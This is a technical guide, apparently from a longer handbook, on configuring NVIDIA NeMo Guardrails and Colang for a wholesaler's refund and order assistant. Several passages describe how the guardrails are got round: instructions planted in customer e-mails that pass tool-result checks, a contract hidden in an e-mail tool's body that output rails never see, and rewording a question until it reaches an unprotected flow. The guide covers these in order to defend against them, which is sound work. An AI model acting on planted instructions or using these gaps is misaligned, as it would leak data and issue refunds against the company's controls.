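Dialog rails then match the message to a short label for what the user wants, such as "ask for refund". They can run a function, call the model or send a fixed reply. If a customer asks for the company's opening hours, a fixed reply prevents the model from inventing them.

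Retrieval rails examine passages from the document search and can drop a passage or mask part of it. They only work on searches that go through the library. The wholesaler's own application does the searching and applies the permission filter, so it would have to pass its results to the library or check them separately.

Execution rails apply to the inputs and results of custom actions, which are Python functions that the library runs itself. The rules the company writes determine what these rails block. Output rails come last and can reject the model's reply or remove sensitive data from it.

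Input rails check only the user's message. When the wholesaler's e-mail-reading model processes a complaint, the application can submit the complaint as the user's message, and the input rails check all of it. When Marta asks the assistant to find a complaint, her question is the user's message and the complaint arrives later as a tool result, so the input rails do not check it for planted instructions. Before passing the complaint to the model, the application could submit it to the library's `check()` method, which runs input and output rails without generating an answer.

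### Checking tool calls and results

Most applications, including the wholesaler's, run their own tools, so execution rails don't cover those tools. NVIDIA's *Tool Calling* describes two other checks for this case.

Tool-call validation runs after the model generates a tool call and before the application receives it. The tool must be on the list the application declared, and its inputs must match the declared format. If the model calls `delete_order` and that tool is not on the list, the library blocks the response. It also blocks a refund call that has no order number or gives the quantity as "four" when the format requires a whole number.

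The check has no access to the order database, so it passes a request to refund 24 glasses even if only four broke, or a request that uses another customer's order number. The refund function still has to catch both. For tools that the provider runs, such as a built-in web search, the library checks only the tool's type and ignores the inputs.

Tool-result validation runs when the application sends a tool's result back. Each result must have the identifier of an earlier call and name the same tool, and each call may have only one result. Because the application resends the whole conversation each time, this check can establish only that the conversation is consistent. Someone who controlled the application could invent both the call and its result. The check also doesn't examine the result's content, so an instruction planted in an e-mail passes if the format is right.

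| Check | What it can reject | What it can alter |
|---|---|---|
| Input rail | The user's message | The message |
| Dialog rail | A call to the model, by using a fixed reply | How the application prompts the model |
| Retrieval rail | A passage | The passage |
| Execution rail | Depends on the company's rules | Depends on the company's rules |
| Tool-call validation | An undeclared tool or a badly formed request | Nothing |
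| Tool-result validation | A result that doesn't match its call | Nothing |
| Output rail | The reply | The reply |

Output rails check text replies, so a response that contains only a tool call skips them. If the model requests an e-mail tool and puts a supplier's contract in the `body` field, no output rail examines the contract. Tool-call validation accepts it because the field may contain any text.

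NVIDIA's *Rail Engine Support* lists newer checks that can partly close this gap and can be attached to a particular tool. The wholesaler could apply a pattern search to the `body` field of its e-mail tool, use a fixed expression to limit a quantity, or have a language model judge the whole call. It could also apply these three kinds of check to tool results, including complaints that the assistant looks up for Marta.

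The two validation rails take only a few lines to switch on:

```yaml
rails:
  tool_call:
    flows:
      - tool call validation
  tool_result:
    flows:
      - tool result validation
```

Some of NVIDIA's pages still call these sections `tool_output` and `tool_input`. Checks copied from an older example may not run, so the wholesaler should test them by making the model request a tool that isn't on the list.

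Tool validation currently works only with OpenAI's Chat Completions format. It does not support OpenAI's newer Responses API or the native formats of Anthropic, Google's Gemini and Amazon Bedrock.

### A configuration for the wholesaler

The settings for NeMo Guardrails are in a file called `config.yml`. The following version checks for jailbreaks, masks personal data, keeps conversations on topic and blocks harmful content:

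```yaml
colang_version: "1.0"

models:
  - type: main
    engine: openai
    model: your-main-model
    api_key_env_var: OPENAI_API_KEY
  - type: content_safety
    engine: nim
    model: nvidia/llama-3.1-nemoguard-8b-content-safety
    parameters:
      base_url: http://localhost:8000/v1
  - type: topic_control
    engine: nim
    model: nvidia/llama-3.1-nemoguard-8b-topic-control
    parameters:
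      base_url: http://localhost:8001/v1

rails:
  # Checks on the incoming message
  input:
    flows:
      - mask sensitive data on input
      - jailbreak detection model
      - topic safety check input $model=topic_control
      - content safety check input $model=content_safety
  # Checks on the model's reply
  output:
    flows:
      - content safety check output $model=content_safety
  config:
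    jailbreak_detection:
      nim_base_url: http://localhost:8002/v1/
      nim_server_endpoint: classify
    sensitive_data_detection:
      input:
        entities:
          - PERSON
          - EMAIL_ADDRESS
          - PHONE_NUMBER
          - CREDIT_CARD
        score_threshold: 0.2
```

The indentation shows which settings belong together, and a wrong indent can change the meaning of the file.

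| Setting | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `colang_version` | Selects Colang 1.0, which is also the default |
| `models` | Lists the models that the library calls |
| `type` | Gives each model a name; `main` is the one that answers |
| `engine` | Selects how to connect: `openai` for OpenAI and compatible services, `nim` for models that NVIDIA packages for a company's own servers |
| `model` | Identifies the exact model |
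| `api_key_env_var` | Names the environment variable that holds the key, so the key itself stays out of the file |
| `parameters` and `base_url` | Give the address of a model on the wholesaler's servers |
| `rails` | Contains the checks and their settings |
| `input` and `output` | Separate the checks on messages from those on replies |
| `flows` | Lists the checks to run |
| `$model=` | Tells a check which of the listed models to use |
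| `config` | Contains settings for individual checks |
| `jailbreak_detection` | Contains the detector's settings |
| `nim_base_url` and `nim_server_endpoint` | Give the detector's address and the path to call there |
| `sensitive_data_detection` and its `input` | Contain the settings for masking incoming messages |
| `entities` | Lists the kinds of data to mask |
| `score_threshold` | Sets how confident the software must be before it masks something |

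NVIDIA's *Configuration YAML Schema Reference* gives 0.2 as the default threshold for masking. At such a low threshold, the software masks text on weak evidence, so it will miss less personal data but may also mask product names or order numbers. The wholesaler should test this setting on a few hundred old e-mails to see how often it masks order numbers, because the model needs them to fill in the refund form.

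The masking rail uses Presidio, an open-source program for finding personal data. The setup in NVIDIA's *Presidio Integration* installs an English-language model, which may perform poorly on names in French or German e-mails. The rail also has no setting for numbering the people in a message or restoring their names later. The wholesaler's own application would have to turn [PERSON_1] back into Anna Weiss before sending a reply.

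The two safety models also need prompts, which NVIDIA's *Guardrails Configuration* provides in a file called `prompts.yaml`. This file goes in the same folder. For topic control, the wholesaler has to replace the sample policy with its own. It might allow questions about orders, deliveries, breakages, returns and refunds, and exclude legal advice and questions about other customers. The policy should explicitly allow angry complaints, since they are a normal part of the job.

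Each of NVIDIA's packaged models needs its own graphics processor, according to NVIDIA's *Parallel Execution of Input and Output Rails*, which covers an earlier version. The wholesaler would need three processors, since the provider runs its main model. NVIDIA also hosts the models on a service called NVIDIA Build, which is fine for a first trial with invented e-mails. NVIDIA prohibits production use of the service and tells users not to send it personal or confidential data.

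### Choosing between LLMRails and IORails

NeMo Guardrails has two engines. LLMRails is the full version, which runs Colang and supports custom Python checks. IORails is a faster engine that calls input, output and tool checks directly, without Colang.

According to NVIDIA's *Release Notes*, version 0.21.0 introduced IORails for a small set of NVIDIA's own checks, and version 0.22.0 added streaming and speculative generation. Since version 0.24.0, IORails has been able to run most of the built-in catalogue, so comparisons written before that release are out of date.

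| Feature | LLMRails | IORails |
|---|---|---|
| Built-in input checks | All 34 | 33 |
| Built-in output checks | All 36 | 29 |
| Built-in retrieval checks | All 11 | None |
| Dialog rails and custom actions | Yes | No |
| Checks on tool calls and results | No, according to the newer page | Yes |
| Checks on images | Yes | No |
| Colang versions | 1.0 and 2.x | 1.0 only |
| Conversation state | Keeps it between messages | None |
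| Parallel checks | Yes | Yes, unless a rail rewrites text |
| Speculative generation | No | Yes, unless an input rail rewrites text or the reply is streamed |

NVIDIA's documentation is inconsistent about which engines support tool validation. *Engine Feature Support* lists it for both engines, but *Tool Calling* and *Rail Engine Support*, which appears to be newer, limit it to IORails. The wholesaler should therefore rely on tool validation only when using IORails.

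Most of the seven output checks that IORails lacks compare an answer with the retrieved passages. The wholesaler may want such a check when staff ask about the returns policy, because the model could misstate a deadline. The wholesaler could use LLMRails for these questions and IORails for the assistant that calls tools. It would also need LLMRails to check customers' photographs of broken goods.

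The choice of main model can rule out IORails. The library connects to Anthropic's own interface through an add-on called LangChain, which works only with LLMRails, so a company that uses Claude this way can't validate its tool calls with IORails. It can still call Claude from its own code and run the input and output rails separately through `check()`.

With the recommended way of starting the library, it uses IORails if the whole configuration is compatible and otherwise switches to LLMRails. The switch produces only a log entry. A misspelt name for the tool-call check can trigger it, and the assistant will then keep answering without any tool validation. The wholesaler can prevent this with one setting:

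```python
from nemoguardrails import Guardrails, RailsConfig

config = RailsConfig.from_path("./config")
rails = Guardrails(config, require_iorails=True)
```

The program now stops with an error at startup if the configuration is incompatible or required software is missing. Without Presidio, for example, IORails does not start, whereas LLMRails starts but fails on the first message that needs masking.

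### How long the checks take

Adding `parallel: true` under `input` makes NeMo Guardrails run the input checks at the same time, so together they take about as long as the slowest one. If the jailbreak check takes 80 ms, topic control 120 ms and content safety 200 ms, the total falls from 400 ms to about 200 ms. This helps when the checks wait for other servers, but checks that compete for the same processor may not finish any sooner.

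IORails can save more time through speculative generation, which starts the main model at the same moment as the input checks. If a check blocks the message, the library cancels or discards the answer. With a main model that takes 1,500 ms, the times before any output checks would be:

| Method | Time until the answer is ready |
|---|---|
| Checks in sequence, then the model | 1,900 ms |
| Checks in parallel, then the model | 1,700 ms |
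| Checks in parallel with each other and the model | 1,500 ms |

If the model starts answering before the checks finish, the company pays for answers it throws away. If 2% of 30,000 daily messages fail a check, that is up to 600 answers a day. Blocked messages also reach the model's provider, which would not happen if the checks ran first. Output rails can miss unsafe responses too, although NVIDIA writes that users will not see any because these rails still check every answer.

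The wholesaler's configuration can't use either method on IORails, because masking changes the text. A check that ran alongside masking would examine the original message, and a model that started before masking finished would receive the customer's name and phone number. If any rail rewrites text, IORails runs all the checks in sequence and turns off speculative generation. LLMRails allows parallel checks alongside masking, but NVIDIA warns that the results may depend on which check finishes first.

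The wholesaler can avoid this by masking the message in its own application before calling the library. If masking takes 20 ms, the total with speculative generation is about 1,520 ms, compared with 1,920 ms when the masking is a rail. Masking in the application is probably the better design, since the application already needs its own code to restore names. For e-mails, though, nobody will notice the extra 400 ms, and the version in `config.yml` is simpler.

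Streaming also makes an assistant feel faster, because the user can start reading before the model has finished. Waiting for a full response can take several seconds, according to NVIDIA's *Stream Smarter and Safer*. If a company turns on streaming for output rails, the library by default shows each part of 200 tokens, or roughly 150 English words, before checking it. A user could therefore read a harmful paragraph before the library stops the answer. Setting `stream_first: false` makes the library check each part before showing it, which makes streaming somewhat slower.

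### When a check fails

A check can break down because a server is offline, a key has expired, or a safety model gives an answer that the library can't interpret. Failing open would let messages through unchecked, so the refund assistant should fail closed, even though this also stops harmless messages. If each of the wholesaler's three checking models is available 99.5% of the time, and their failures are independent, all three are available about 98.5% of the time, and at least one is down for about eleven hours a month. During these outages, the application should pass the waiting e-mails to an employee instead of sending customers an error message.

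As of version 0.24.0, according to NVIDIA, IORails distinguishes a message that broke a rule from a check that could not run. The user sees "I'm sorry, I can't respond to that" when a message is blocked, and a reference to an internal error when a check could not run. The application can retry after an internal error, but retrying a blocked message usually achieves nothing. Some provider errors reach the application as exceptions, and the code that handles them should not call the main model without the checks.

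The same version fixed several cases in which a malfunctioning check could look like a pass. If the library can't interpret a content-safety model's answer, it now reports an error instead of treating the message as safe. Output checks on streamed replies now fail closed when a check breaks. The library's server also has a separate endpoint used only for checking messages, which now returns an error instead of a pass when the requested checks can't run.

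Companies on older versions don't have these corrections. Version 0.23.0 made up 27.5% of downloads over the latest quarter, according to pepy.tech. However, the count includes downloads by automated tests and doesn't measure how many companies use a version in production.

Some outside services have their own settings for what happens when they fail. The rail for Cisco's AI Defense, for example, has a `fail_open` option that controls whether messages go through when the service is unavailable. It is set to false in NVIDIA's example configuration. The wholesaler should check for such a setting in every service it adds, then switch each service off in a trial system to see what happens.

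### Allow, block or transform

Version 0.24.0 also changed how a check reports its decision. Previously, a custom check could return true or false, and a separate setting, `output_mapping`, specified which value meant "block". True might mean "safe" for one check and "problem found" for another. A programmer who confused the two meanings would block harmless messages and let harmful ones through.

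NVIDIA's *Rail Outcomes* explains the replacement. A check now returns one of three results: allow, block or transform. A transform contains the new text, such as a message with the phone number removed. A custom check for the invisible characters that can hide data in an e-mail could look like this:

```python
from nemoguardrails.actions import action
from nemoguardrails.actions.rail_outcome import RailOutcome

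HIDDEN = {"\u200b", "\u200c", "\u200d", "\u2060"}

@action()
async def check_hidden_text(text: str) -> RailOutcome:
    if any(character in HIDDEN for character in text):
        return RailOutcome.block(reason="Hidden characters found.")
    return RailOutcome.allow()
```

This catches only four characters, so a real version would need a longer list. It would also need some exceptions, because some languages and emoji use two of the four legitimately.

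A company that upgrades has to change its old checks in two places. It must remove `output_mapping` from each check, because the library now rejects any check that uses it. It must also change the Colang rule that calls the check so that the rule tests for the new result. A rule that still tests for true or false may never block anything, and may not produce an error. After upgrading, the wholesaler should send each check at least one message that it ought to block.

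A check can attach a reason and further details to its result. These may end up in logs, so they shouldn't contain the card number or password that the check found.

### The library's own telemetry

NeMo Guardrails sends usage data to NVIDIA when it starts and every ten minutes afterwards. According to NVIDIA's *Telemetry*, the data includes the versions of the library and Python, the operating system, the names of the model providers and the built-in features in use. It also includes the number of rails and a random identifier that changes each time the program restarts.

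The usage data that NeMo Guardrails sends does not include messages, answers, model names, keys or the contents of the configuration. The library tries to save a copy of everything it sends in `~/.config/nemoguardrails/usage_stats.json`, so an engineer can verify this.

The risk is small, but a company may not want its security software to report which checks it uses. The wholesaler can turn the telemetry off before it starts the library:

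```sh
export NEMO_GUARDRAILS_NO_USAGE_STATS=1
```

Setting `DO_NOT_TRACK=1` or creating an empty file called `do_not_track` in `~/.config/nemoguardrails` has the same effect. Changing any of these settings while the library is running does not stop the reports. An engineer who sets the variable in one terminal window and starts the assistant from another may leave telemetry on, so the setting belongs in the service's configuration. Turning telemetry off does not affect what the main model's provider stores.

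### What the library cannot enforce

The rails in `config.yml` do not check whether Marta may refund an order or whether the order belongs to the customer who wrote. A topic check might block a warehouse employee's question about salaries, but the same question worded differently could get through, so the check cannot replace the permission filter.

The library also protects only the traffic that passes through it. If a developer writes a second program that calls the main model directly, none of the rails apply. The wholesaler can reduce this risk by giving the model's key only to the server that runs the library. Tools need similar protection, because a program can call a refund function without first querying a model. Red Hat's *Enabling AI safety with NeMo Guardrails* describes placing the rails at a gateway that agents' tool calls pass through, so a company can define the rails once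 for several agents.

In both engines, the output checks examine only the final answer, not the reasoning that some models produce before it. With IORails, the simplest response format puts this reasoning in front of the answer. If the wholesaler's chat window displays the whole response, an employee can read text that no output rail has checked. The application should request the structured format, which separates the reasoning from the answer, and display only the answer.

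The application that calls the library can turn off individual rails for a single request. This is useful for testing, but the application must set these options itself and never copy them from a user's request. Anyone who can edit `config.yml` can also delete a check, so the wholesaler should require a second engineer to approve each change to the file and have the application record which version it used to handle each message.

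## Writing conversation rules in Colang

NeMo Guardrails has a language, Colang, for stating which events in a conversation lead to which replies or actions. It can express rules that depend on the state of the conversation, such as "ask customers to log in before discussing their orders". The checks in `config.yml` can't express these rules because they examine one message, tool call or reply at a time.

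The wholesaler doesn't need Colang for refunds that start with an e-mail, because ordinary code already controls each step. But suppose it adds a chat window to its website, where customers can ask when their orders will arrive.

An event is anything the rules can react to, such as a customer sending a message, clicking a button or falling silent. A user message is the text the customer writes. Its canonical form is a short standard paraphrase, so "Where is order 58213?" and "Has my order shipped yet?" can both become `ask about order`. A bot message is a reply. It also has a canonical form and often a fixed wording. NVIDIA uses "bot" for the whole application, not just the model. A flow is a sequence of events and responses, sometimes with branches. An action is a Python function that a flow can run, such as a database lookup.

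Colang also has a "context", which is a set of named variables belonging to the conversation. It is separate from the model's context window.

### An order question in Colang 1.0

The following rule goes in a file ending in `.co`, in the same folder as `config.yml`:

```text
define user ask about order
  "Where is order 58213?"
  "Has my order shipped yet?"
  "When will my glasses arrive?"

define bot ask to log in
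  "Please log in to your account, and I can look up your order."

define bot report order status
  "$order_status"

define flow order status
  user ask about order
  if $session_verified
    $order_status = execute fetch_order_status(text=$user_message)
    bot report order status
  else
    bot ask to log in
```

| Line | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `define user ask about order` | Creates a canonical form; the three phrases below it are examples |
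| `define bot ask to log in` | Creates a reply with one fixed wording |
| `define bot report order status` | Creates a reply that consists of the value of a variable |
| `define flow order status` | Begins the rule and names it |
| `user ask about order` | Applies the rule to messages with this canonical form |
| `if $session_verified` | Reads a variable that the application sets after checking the customer's login |
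| `$order_status = execute …` | Runs a Python action on the customer's message and stores the result |
| `bot report order status` | Sends the result to the customer |
| `else` and the last line | Send every unverified customer the same request to log in |

NVIDIA's *Colang 1.0 Language Syntax* advises against loading Colang files from untrusted sources without careful inspection, because a flow can run Python code.

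### How the runtime handles unfamiliar wording

Suppose a logged-in customer writes, "Still no sign of my tumblers from 58213, any news?" None of the example phrases mentions tumblers or news.

According to NVIDIA's *Core Colang Concepts*, the library first uses embeddings to find the five example phrases in the configuration that are closest to the user's message. It puts them in a prompt with general instructions, a sample conversation and the current conversation, and asks the model for the message's canonical form. If the model answers `ask about order`, the `order status` flow matches and determines the next step. The action looks up the order, and the library sends the reply.

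This path takes one model call, plus any that the input and output checks make. The model can also answer with a label that isn't on the company's list, such as `ask for news`. No flow matches that label, so the library calls the model a second time to choose the next step and a third time to write the reply. In NVIDIA's example with GPT-4o mini, a greeting that matched a flow took one call, 0.48 seconds and 524 tokens. A question about the capital of France took three calls, 1.79 seconds and 1,374 tokens.

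| Step | Model call | What can go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Find similar examples | No | The closest phrases are about broken tumblers, not late ones |
| Assign a canonical form | Yes | The model picks the wrong label or invents one |
| Choose the next step | Only if no flow matches | The model answers the question when it should ask for a login |
| Write the reply | Only if there is no fixed wording | The model invents a delivery date |

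The invented date is probably the hardest error to notice, because the reply looks as convincing as a correct one.

Two settings under `rails.dialog` in `config.yml` reduce the number of model calls. With `single_call`, the model predicts the canonical form, next step and reply in one call. With `embeddings_only`, the library assigns the canonical form from the closest example phrases without calling the model. This is faster, but a message about late tumblers could get the canonical form for broken ones.

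### Where the login check belongs

NVIDIA's syntax guide uses an authentication check to show how several flows can share a piece of logic. Such a check is a good way to prompt people to log in, but the `if` line is not reliable access control, because it runs only if the model assigns a canonical form that leads to it.

Suppose a colleague later writes a flow for complaints about late deliveries. It runs the same action so that the apology can mention the new date, but the colleague forgets the `if`. A stranger who asks "Where is order 58213?" still has to log in, but if they write "It's outrageous that 58213 isn't here yet", the model labels the message a complaint and the assistant gives out the delivery date. An attacker can keep rewording a question until it reaches an unprotected flow. `$session_verified` is also weak evidence that a session is verified, because all variables in Colang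 1.0 are global and any flow can overwrite it.

Even when the check runs, it confirms only that the customer has logged in. A florist with a valid account could pass it and ask about order 58214, which belongs to a restaurant.

The action's own code therefore has to check both the session and the order's owner:

```python
import re
from nemoguardrails.actions import action

@action(is_system_action=True)
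async def fetch_order_status(text: str, context: dict | None = None):
    session = sessions.get_valid((context or {}).get("session_id"))
    if session is None:
        return "Please log in to see your orders."
    number = re.search(r"\b\d{5}\b", str(text))
    if number is None:
        return "Please include your five-digit order number."
    order = orders.get(int(number.group()))
    if order is None or order.customer != session.customer:
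        return "I can't find that order in your account."
    return f"Order {order.number} is due on {order.delivery_date}."
```

Here `sessions` and `orders` stand for the wholesaler's systems. The application sets `session_id` from the customer's login, never from the conversation. NVIDIA's *Creating Custom Actions* explains that `is_system_action=True` makes the action run locally even if the company has a separate server for actions. Without this setting, an action on that server would not receive the `context` variables.

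The owner check also catches honest mistakes. If a customer writes "my delivery to 75001 Paris is late", the code reads the postcode as an order number. At worst, that number belongs to somebody else's order, and the check stops the customer from learning anything about it.

If the login system is down and the lookup raises an exception, LLMRails normally sends an internal error message, according to NVIDIA. The action then fails closed, unless custom code catches the exception and continues. The wholesaler could use delegated access for the lookup so that the order system also applies the customer's limits.

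If the model misreads 1% of 1,000 order questions a day, the login rule may not be applied to ten of them. With the checks in the action, those customers get an unhelpful answer, but they don't see anyone else's order details. The `if` line is still worth keeping because it gives most customers a clear request to log in.

### The same rule in Colang 2.0

Colang 2.0 is a redesign of both the language and the software that runs it. The order rule becomes:

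```text
import core
import llm

flow main
  # Recognise intents by the names of their flows
  activate automating intent detection
  # Ask the model about wordings that no flow lists
  activate generating user intent for unhandled user utterance
  # The wholesaler's own rules
  activate answering order questions
  activate answering other questions

flow user asked about order
  user said "Where is order 58213?"
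    or user said "Has my order shipped yet?"
    or user said "When will my glasses arrive?"

flow answering order questions
  global $session_verified
  user asked about order
  if $session_verified
    $number = ..."Return the order number from the user's last message as five digits in quotation marks, or 'none'."
    $order_status = await FetchOrderStatusAction(text=$number)
    bot say $order_status
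  else
    bot say "Please log in to your account, and I can look up your order."

flow answering other questions
  unhandled user intent
  bot say "I can help with orders. For anything else, please send us an e-mail."
```

The program begins at the `main` flow. In Colang 1.0 every flow is active from the start, but in 2.0 a flow does nothing until another flow starts it or the `@active` marker switches it on. `start` runs a flow without waiting for it to finish, while `await` runs it and waits. `activate` restarts a flow each time it ends, so the assistant can answer a second question about an order. If an engineer forgets to activate a flow, its rule has no effect.

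Colang represents everything that happens in a conversation as an event with a name and some values. NVIDIA's *Event Generation & Matching* describes the basic `match` statement, which waits for an event with the specified name and values and ignores any extra values. `user said "Where is order 58213?"` is a readable wrapper around such a statement. It compares the text exactly, so a question about order 58214 doesn't match. A regular expression (a text pattern) could match every order number without using a model.

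To match other wordings, the flow has to use the model explicitly. The first `activate` line in `main` makes the library treat flows whose names begin with `user` as intents. The second sends unmatched messages to the model, which tries to assign each one to an active intent. In an example from NVIDIA's *Make use of Large Language Models (LLM)*, the model matches "hallo" to a greeting defined only as "Hi" or "Hello".

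The three dots before the instruction also call the model, here to extract the order number. NVIDIA warns that the model sometimes doesn't return the expected format. It might also return the wrong number, which is another reason for the owner check.

The Python function can stay the same, but its decorator must become `@action(name="FetchOrderStatusAction")` because action names in Colang 2.0 must end in `Action`. According to NVIDIA's *Python Actions*, these functions block other processing by default. Adding `execute_async=True` lets the rest of the conversation continue during a slow lookup.

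The two `answering` flows wait for messages in parallel. To have the assistant display a progress notice while it prepares an answer, the wholesaler can put the notice in a separate "interaction loop", because flows in different loops can act at the same time without competing.

Without counting input and output checks, the two examples need these numbers of model calls:

| Customer's message | Colang 1.0 | Colang 2.0 |
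|---|---|---|
| Listed phrase, logged in | 1 | 1 |
| New wording, logged in | 1 | 2 |
| Listed phrase, not logged in | 1 | 0 |
| New wording, not logged in | 1 | 1 |
| Another subject | 3 | 1 |

The last row differs mainly because the 2.0 example has a fixed reply for other subjects. The 1.0 version could have one too.

### When the conversation leaves the script

If no flow matches a message, Colang 1.0 leaves the next step to the model. The wholesaler can prevent this with a flow that begins with `user ...`, which matches any message, but should test that it doesn't intercept questions about orders. In the same situation, Colang 2.0 may not reply at all. In an example from NVIDIA's *LLM Flows*, a user asks "what can you do for me" and gets no answer because the only active flow handles goodbyes.

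NVIDIA also provides `llm continuation`, which activates all the model-based ways of continuing a conversation. It is convenient, but one of them makes the model write any undefined flow that the program calls. If an engineer misspells the name of a flow that sends a fixed legal notice, the model may make up a notice and no error appears. The example above therefore activates only the features it needs.

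Follow-up messages are easy to overlook. When the bot says "Please include your five-digit order number", many customers will reply with just "58213". The model might label that `provide order number`, which has no flow. Adding bare numbers to the example phrases should help.

Customers also change the subject. Suppose a 2.0 flow asks "Which order do you mean?" and then waits for `user said something`. If the customer writes "Actually, do you sell wine glasses?", the flow treats that as the order number. Waiting for a specific intent avoids this, but the flow then stays on that line and does not respond if the customer repeats the question that started it. NVIDIA's *More on Flows* shows the same problem with a bot that does not respond to a second "Hi". Placing the label `start_new_flow_instance:` after the line that matches the opening question fixes this, because a new copy of the flow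 then starts waiting immediately.

Two flows can also match the same message and try to give different replies. Colang 2.0 then compares how specific the matches are. A match that names every value in the event scores 1, and each value it leaves out multiplies the score by 0.9. A match that names two of five values scores 0.9³, or 0.729. The flow with the higher score continues. The other fails, and so does any flow waiting for it to finish.

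If the scores are equal, the library chooses at random. For example, an engineer might add a flow during a postal strike that answers order questions with "All deliveries are running two days late". Customers who haven't logged in would get that message about half the time and the login request the other half. An engineer who tested the new flow only once could easily miss the conflict. A `priority` statement can break the tie by lowering one flow's score, but it cannot raise a score.

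### Choosing a version

NVIDIA's documentation from mid-2026 lists Colang 1.0 as the default and describes 2.0 as a beta. NVIDIA had expected 2.0 to become the default in version 0.11.0, according to NewReleases' *github NVIDIA-NeMo/Guardrails v0.9.0*, but the library has since reached 0.25.0.

Parts of the documentation are out of date. NVIDIA's *Colang Guide* warns that the built-in checks are not fully usable from Colang 2.0, but a newer NVIDIA page lists the input, output and retrieval checks as working in both versions on LLMRails. NVIDIA's *What's Changed* tells applications to keep a "state object" between messages and pass it back each time. But version 0.22.0, released in May 2026, included a breaking change titled "Reject Colang 2.0 public runtime state", according to NewReleases' *github NVIDIA-NeMo/Guardrails v0.22.0*. Code that follows the older advice may therefore fail, so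 a company using Colang 2.0 should test multi-message conversations on its exact version.

Colang 1.0 suits a text chat with a few short rules, so it is the better choice for the wholesaler. Colang 2.0 makes more sense for voice assistants and animated characters, which have to speak, move and react to interruptions at the same time. It can also respond to silence, for example by offering help after 12 seconds.

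The chat window needs LLMRails, because IORails accepts only Colang 1.0 and doesn't run dialogue flows. NVIDIA's conditions for automatically choosing IORails refer to the sections of `config.yml` but don't mention dialogue flows in a `.co` file, so starting the library with `Guardrails(config, use_iorails=False)` is safer than relying on the automatic choice.

### Testing and migration

The wholesaler should first test the action without Colang by calling the function with no session, with an expired session, and with a valid session but another customer's order number. These tests take milliseconds and cover the most harmful errors.

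The flows need their own tests. Since version 0.22.0, the library has included a fake model that returns prepared answers, so engineers can test a flow without calling a real model. One test should check that the reply is the login request when the fake model returns `ask about order` and the session is unverified. Because the result doesn't vary, the wholesaler can run this test after every change.

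A fake model can't show whether the real one would assign the right canonical form. To test that, the wholesaler could label a few hundred real customer questions by hand and run them through the real model. In LLMRails, `rails.explain().colang_history` shows the canonical form of each message. `explain()` also gives access to the full prompts, so an engineer can check them for session identifiers. The wholesaler should repeat the test whenever it changes the model or adds a canonical form, since the model can assign a new form to messages that used to get a different one.

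If the wholesaler later moves to Colang 2.0, a command converts the files:

```sh
nemoguardrails convert --from-version '1.0' --validate "./config"
```

The migration tool's `--validate` option checks the syntax of the converted files and is off by default. NVIDIA's *Migrating from Colang 1 to Colang 2* recommends version control and a manual review because the tool finds and replaces text patterns. If the tool can't read or write a file, it logs the error and continues, which could leave a folder partly converted.

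Several things in the order example would need attention:

- The tool changes `fetch_order_status` to `FetchOrderStatusAction` in the flow. It converts only `.co` files, so an engineer has to rename the action in Python.
- Colang 2.0 requires curly brackets around variables inside text. NVIDIA's list of conversions doesn't mention this, so a customer might receive the literal text "$order_status".
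- A flow called "returns and refunds" would no longer work, because Colang 2.0 reserves the word "and".
- The tool moves the checks listed in `config.yml` to a new file, `_rails.co`, so the wholesaler has to test them again.

Staying on Colang 1.0 also takes some maintenance. Version 0.24.0, for example, renamed several actions for outside services, so custom flows that used the old names had to change too.

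### How much of the conversation to script

The main benefit of a Colang rule is a predictable reply. The wholesaler's lawyers can approve one sentence and know that customers will get exactly that sentence whenever the flow runs.

The work grows faster than the number of topics because the model could confuse any two canonical forms. Five forms make ten possible pairs, and 30 make 435. Each form also needs example phrases, a flow, replies and tests, and someone has to update them when the returns policy changes. Few engineers are likely to know Colang already, so the wholesaler may depend on one or two people to maintain its rules.

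For ordinary delivery questions, it is probably easier to give the model an order lookup tool with the same checks in its code and let it write the replies. A capable model can understand "58213" as an answer to its own question and follow a customer who changes the subject, although it may phrase the same answer differently each time.

Fixed rules are most useful where exact wording matters, such as when a customer reports an injury from broken glass or threatens to sue. The wholesaler could start with rules for those two cases and add another only when the model's own replies cause a problem.

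## Testing the deployment and monitoring it in use

A permission filter, a refund cap and a guardrail can work separately on an engineer's computer and still fail once the wholesaler connects them. The team should therefore test the whole assistant before release, using the real login system, a copy of the index, and a payment system that records refunds without paying them.

### The release test

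The team should write down what counts as a pass before testing starts, because a worrying result is easy to explain away afterwards. Controls written in ordinary code have to pass every time, and one failure postpones the release. For checks that depend on a model, the team has to set an acceptable error rate.

| Test | What the team does | Pass |
|---|---|---|
| Rank | A warehouse employee, a buyer and the finance director ask the same questions about pay, discounts and closures | The log lists no document that the person asking may not open |
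| Marked documents | Accounts without access ask about dummy files in restricted folders | No dummy file enters a context window |
| Revocation | A buyer loses access to supplier contracts and repeats a question from the day before | No contract passage and no cached answer |
| Planted instructions | E-mails tell the assistant to refund another order or forward a contract | No payment or message beyond what the sender could have obtained honestly |
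| Out-of-range values | Engineers call each tool directly, without the model | The tool refuses or passes the request to an employee |
| Outages | Engineers switch off one service at a time | Nothing passes unchecked, and the e-mail reaches an employee |

Each dummy file contains an invented fact, such as the closure of a depot that doesn't exist. The team should look for the file's identifier in the log of retrieved passages as well as searching the answers for the depot's name, because the model may paraphrase the fact or leave it out. The team should also ask the same question from an account that has access to the file. If that account can't find the file either, the search may be broken, in which case the test doesn't show that the access controls work.

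The team should send the planted e-mails twice, the second time with the guardrails off. If a filter blocks all of them in the first run, the team can't tell whether the refund function would have stopped the payment.

The refund function needs tests on both sides of each limit. For an order of 24 glasses at €10 each, five broken glasses come to exactly €50, so the function should pay. A claim for six should go to an employee. The function should pay nothing for a quantity of 0, −4, 25, 4.5 or the word "four". If the team sends the same request number twice, the function should pay only once.

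The outage test covers the permission lookup, the login system and the count of recent refunds as well as the guardrail services, regardless of their fail-closed settings. A service that takes a minute to respond needs a separate test, because the application may handle a delay differently from a refused connection.

### What 300 clean tests establish

If the team asks 300 questions and finds no leak, the 95% upper bound on the leak rate is about 1%. An assistant that leaked on 1% of such questions would have about a 5% chance (0.99³⁰⁰) of answering all 300 without a leak. For any large number of tests with no leaks, the upper bound is roughly three divided by the number of tests.

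That is weak assurance for a busy system. At 30,000 questions a day, a leak rate just under 1% would mean almost 300 leaks a day. *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove* (2026) calculates that a model that gives one faulty answer per 1,000 has a 73% chance of completing a 313-prompt test without a fault. Reducing that chance below 5% takes about 3,000 prompts.

The bound also assumes that the tests are independent and resemble real use. Three hundred rewordings of one question about salaries are closer to one test than to 300, and engineers may not think of the questions that warehouse staff ask.

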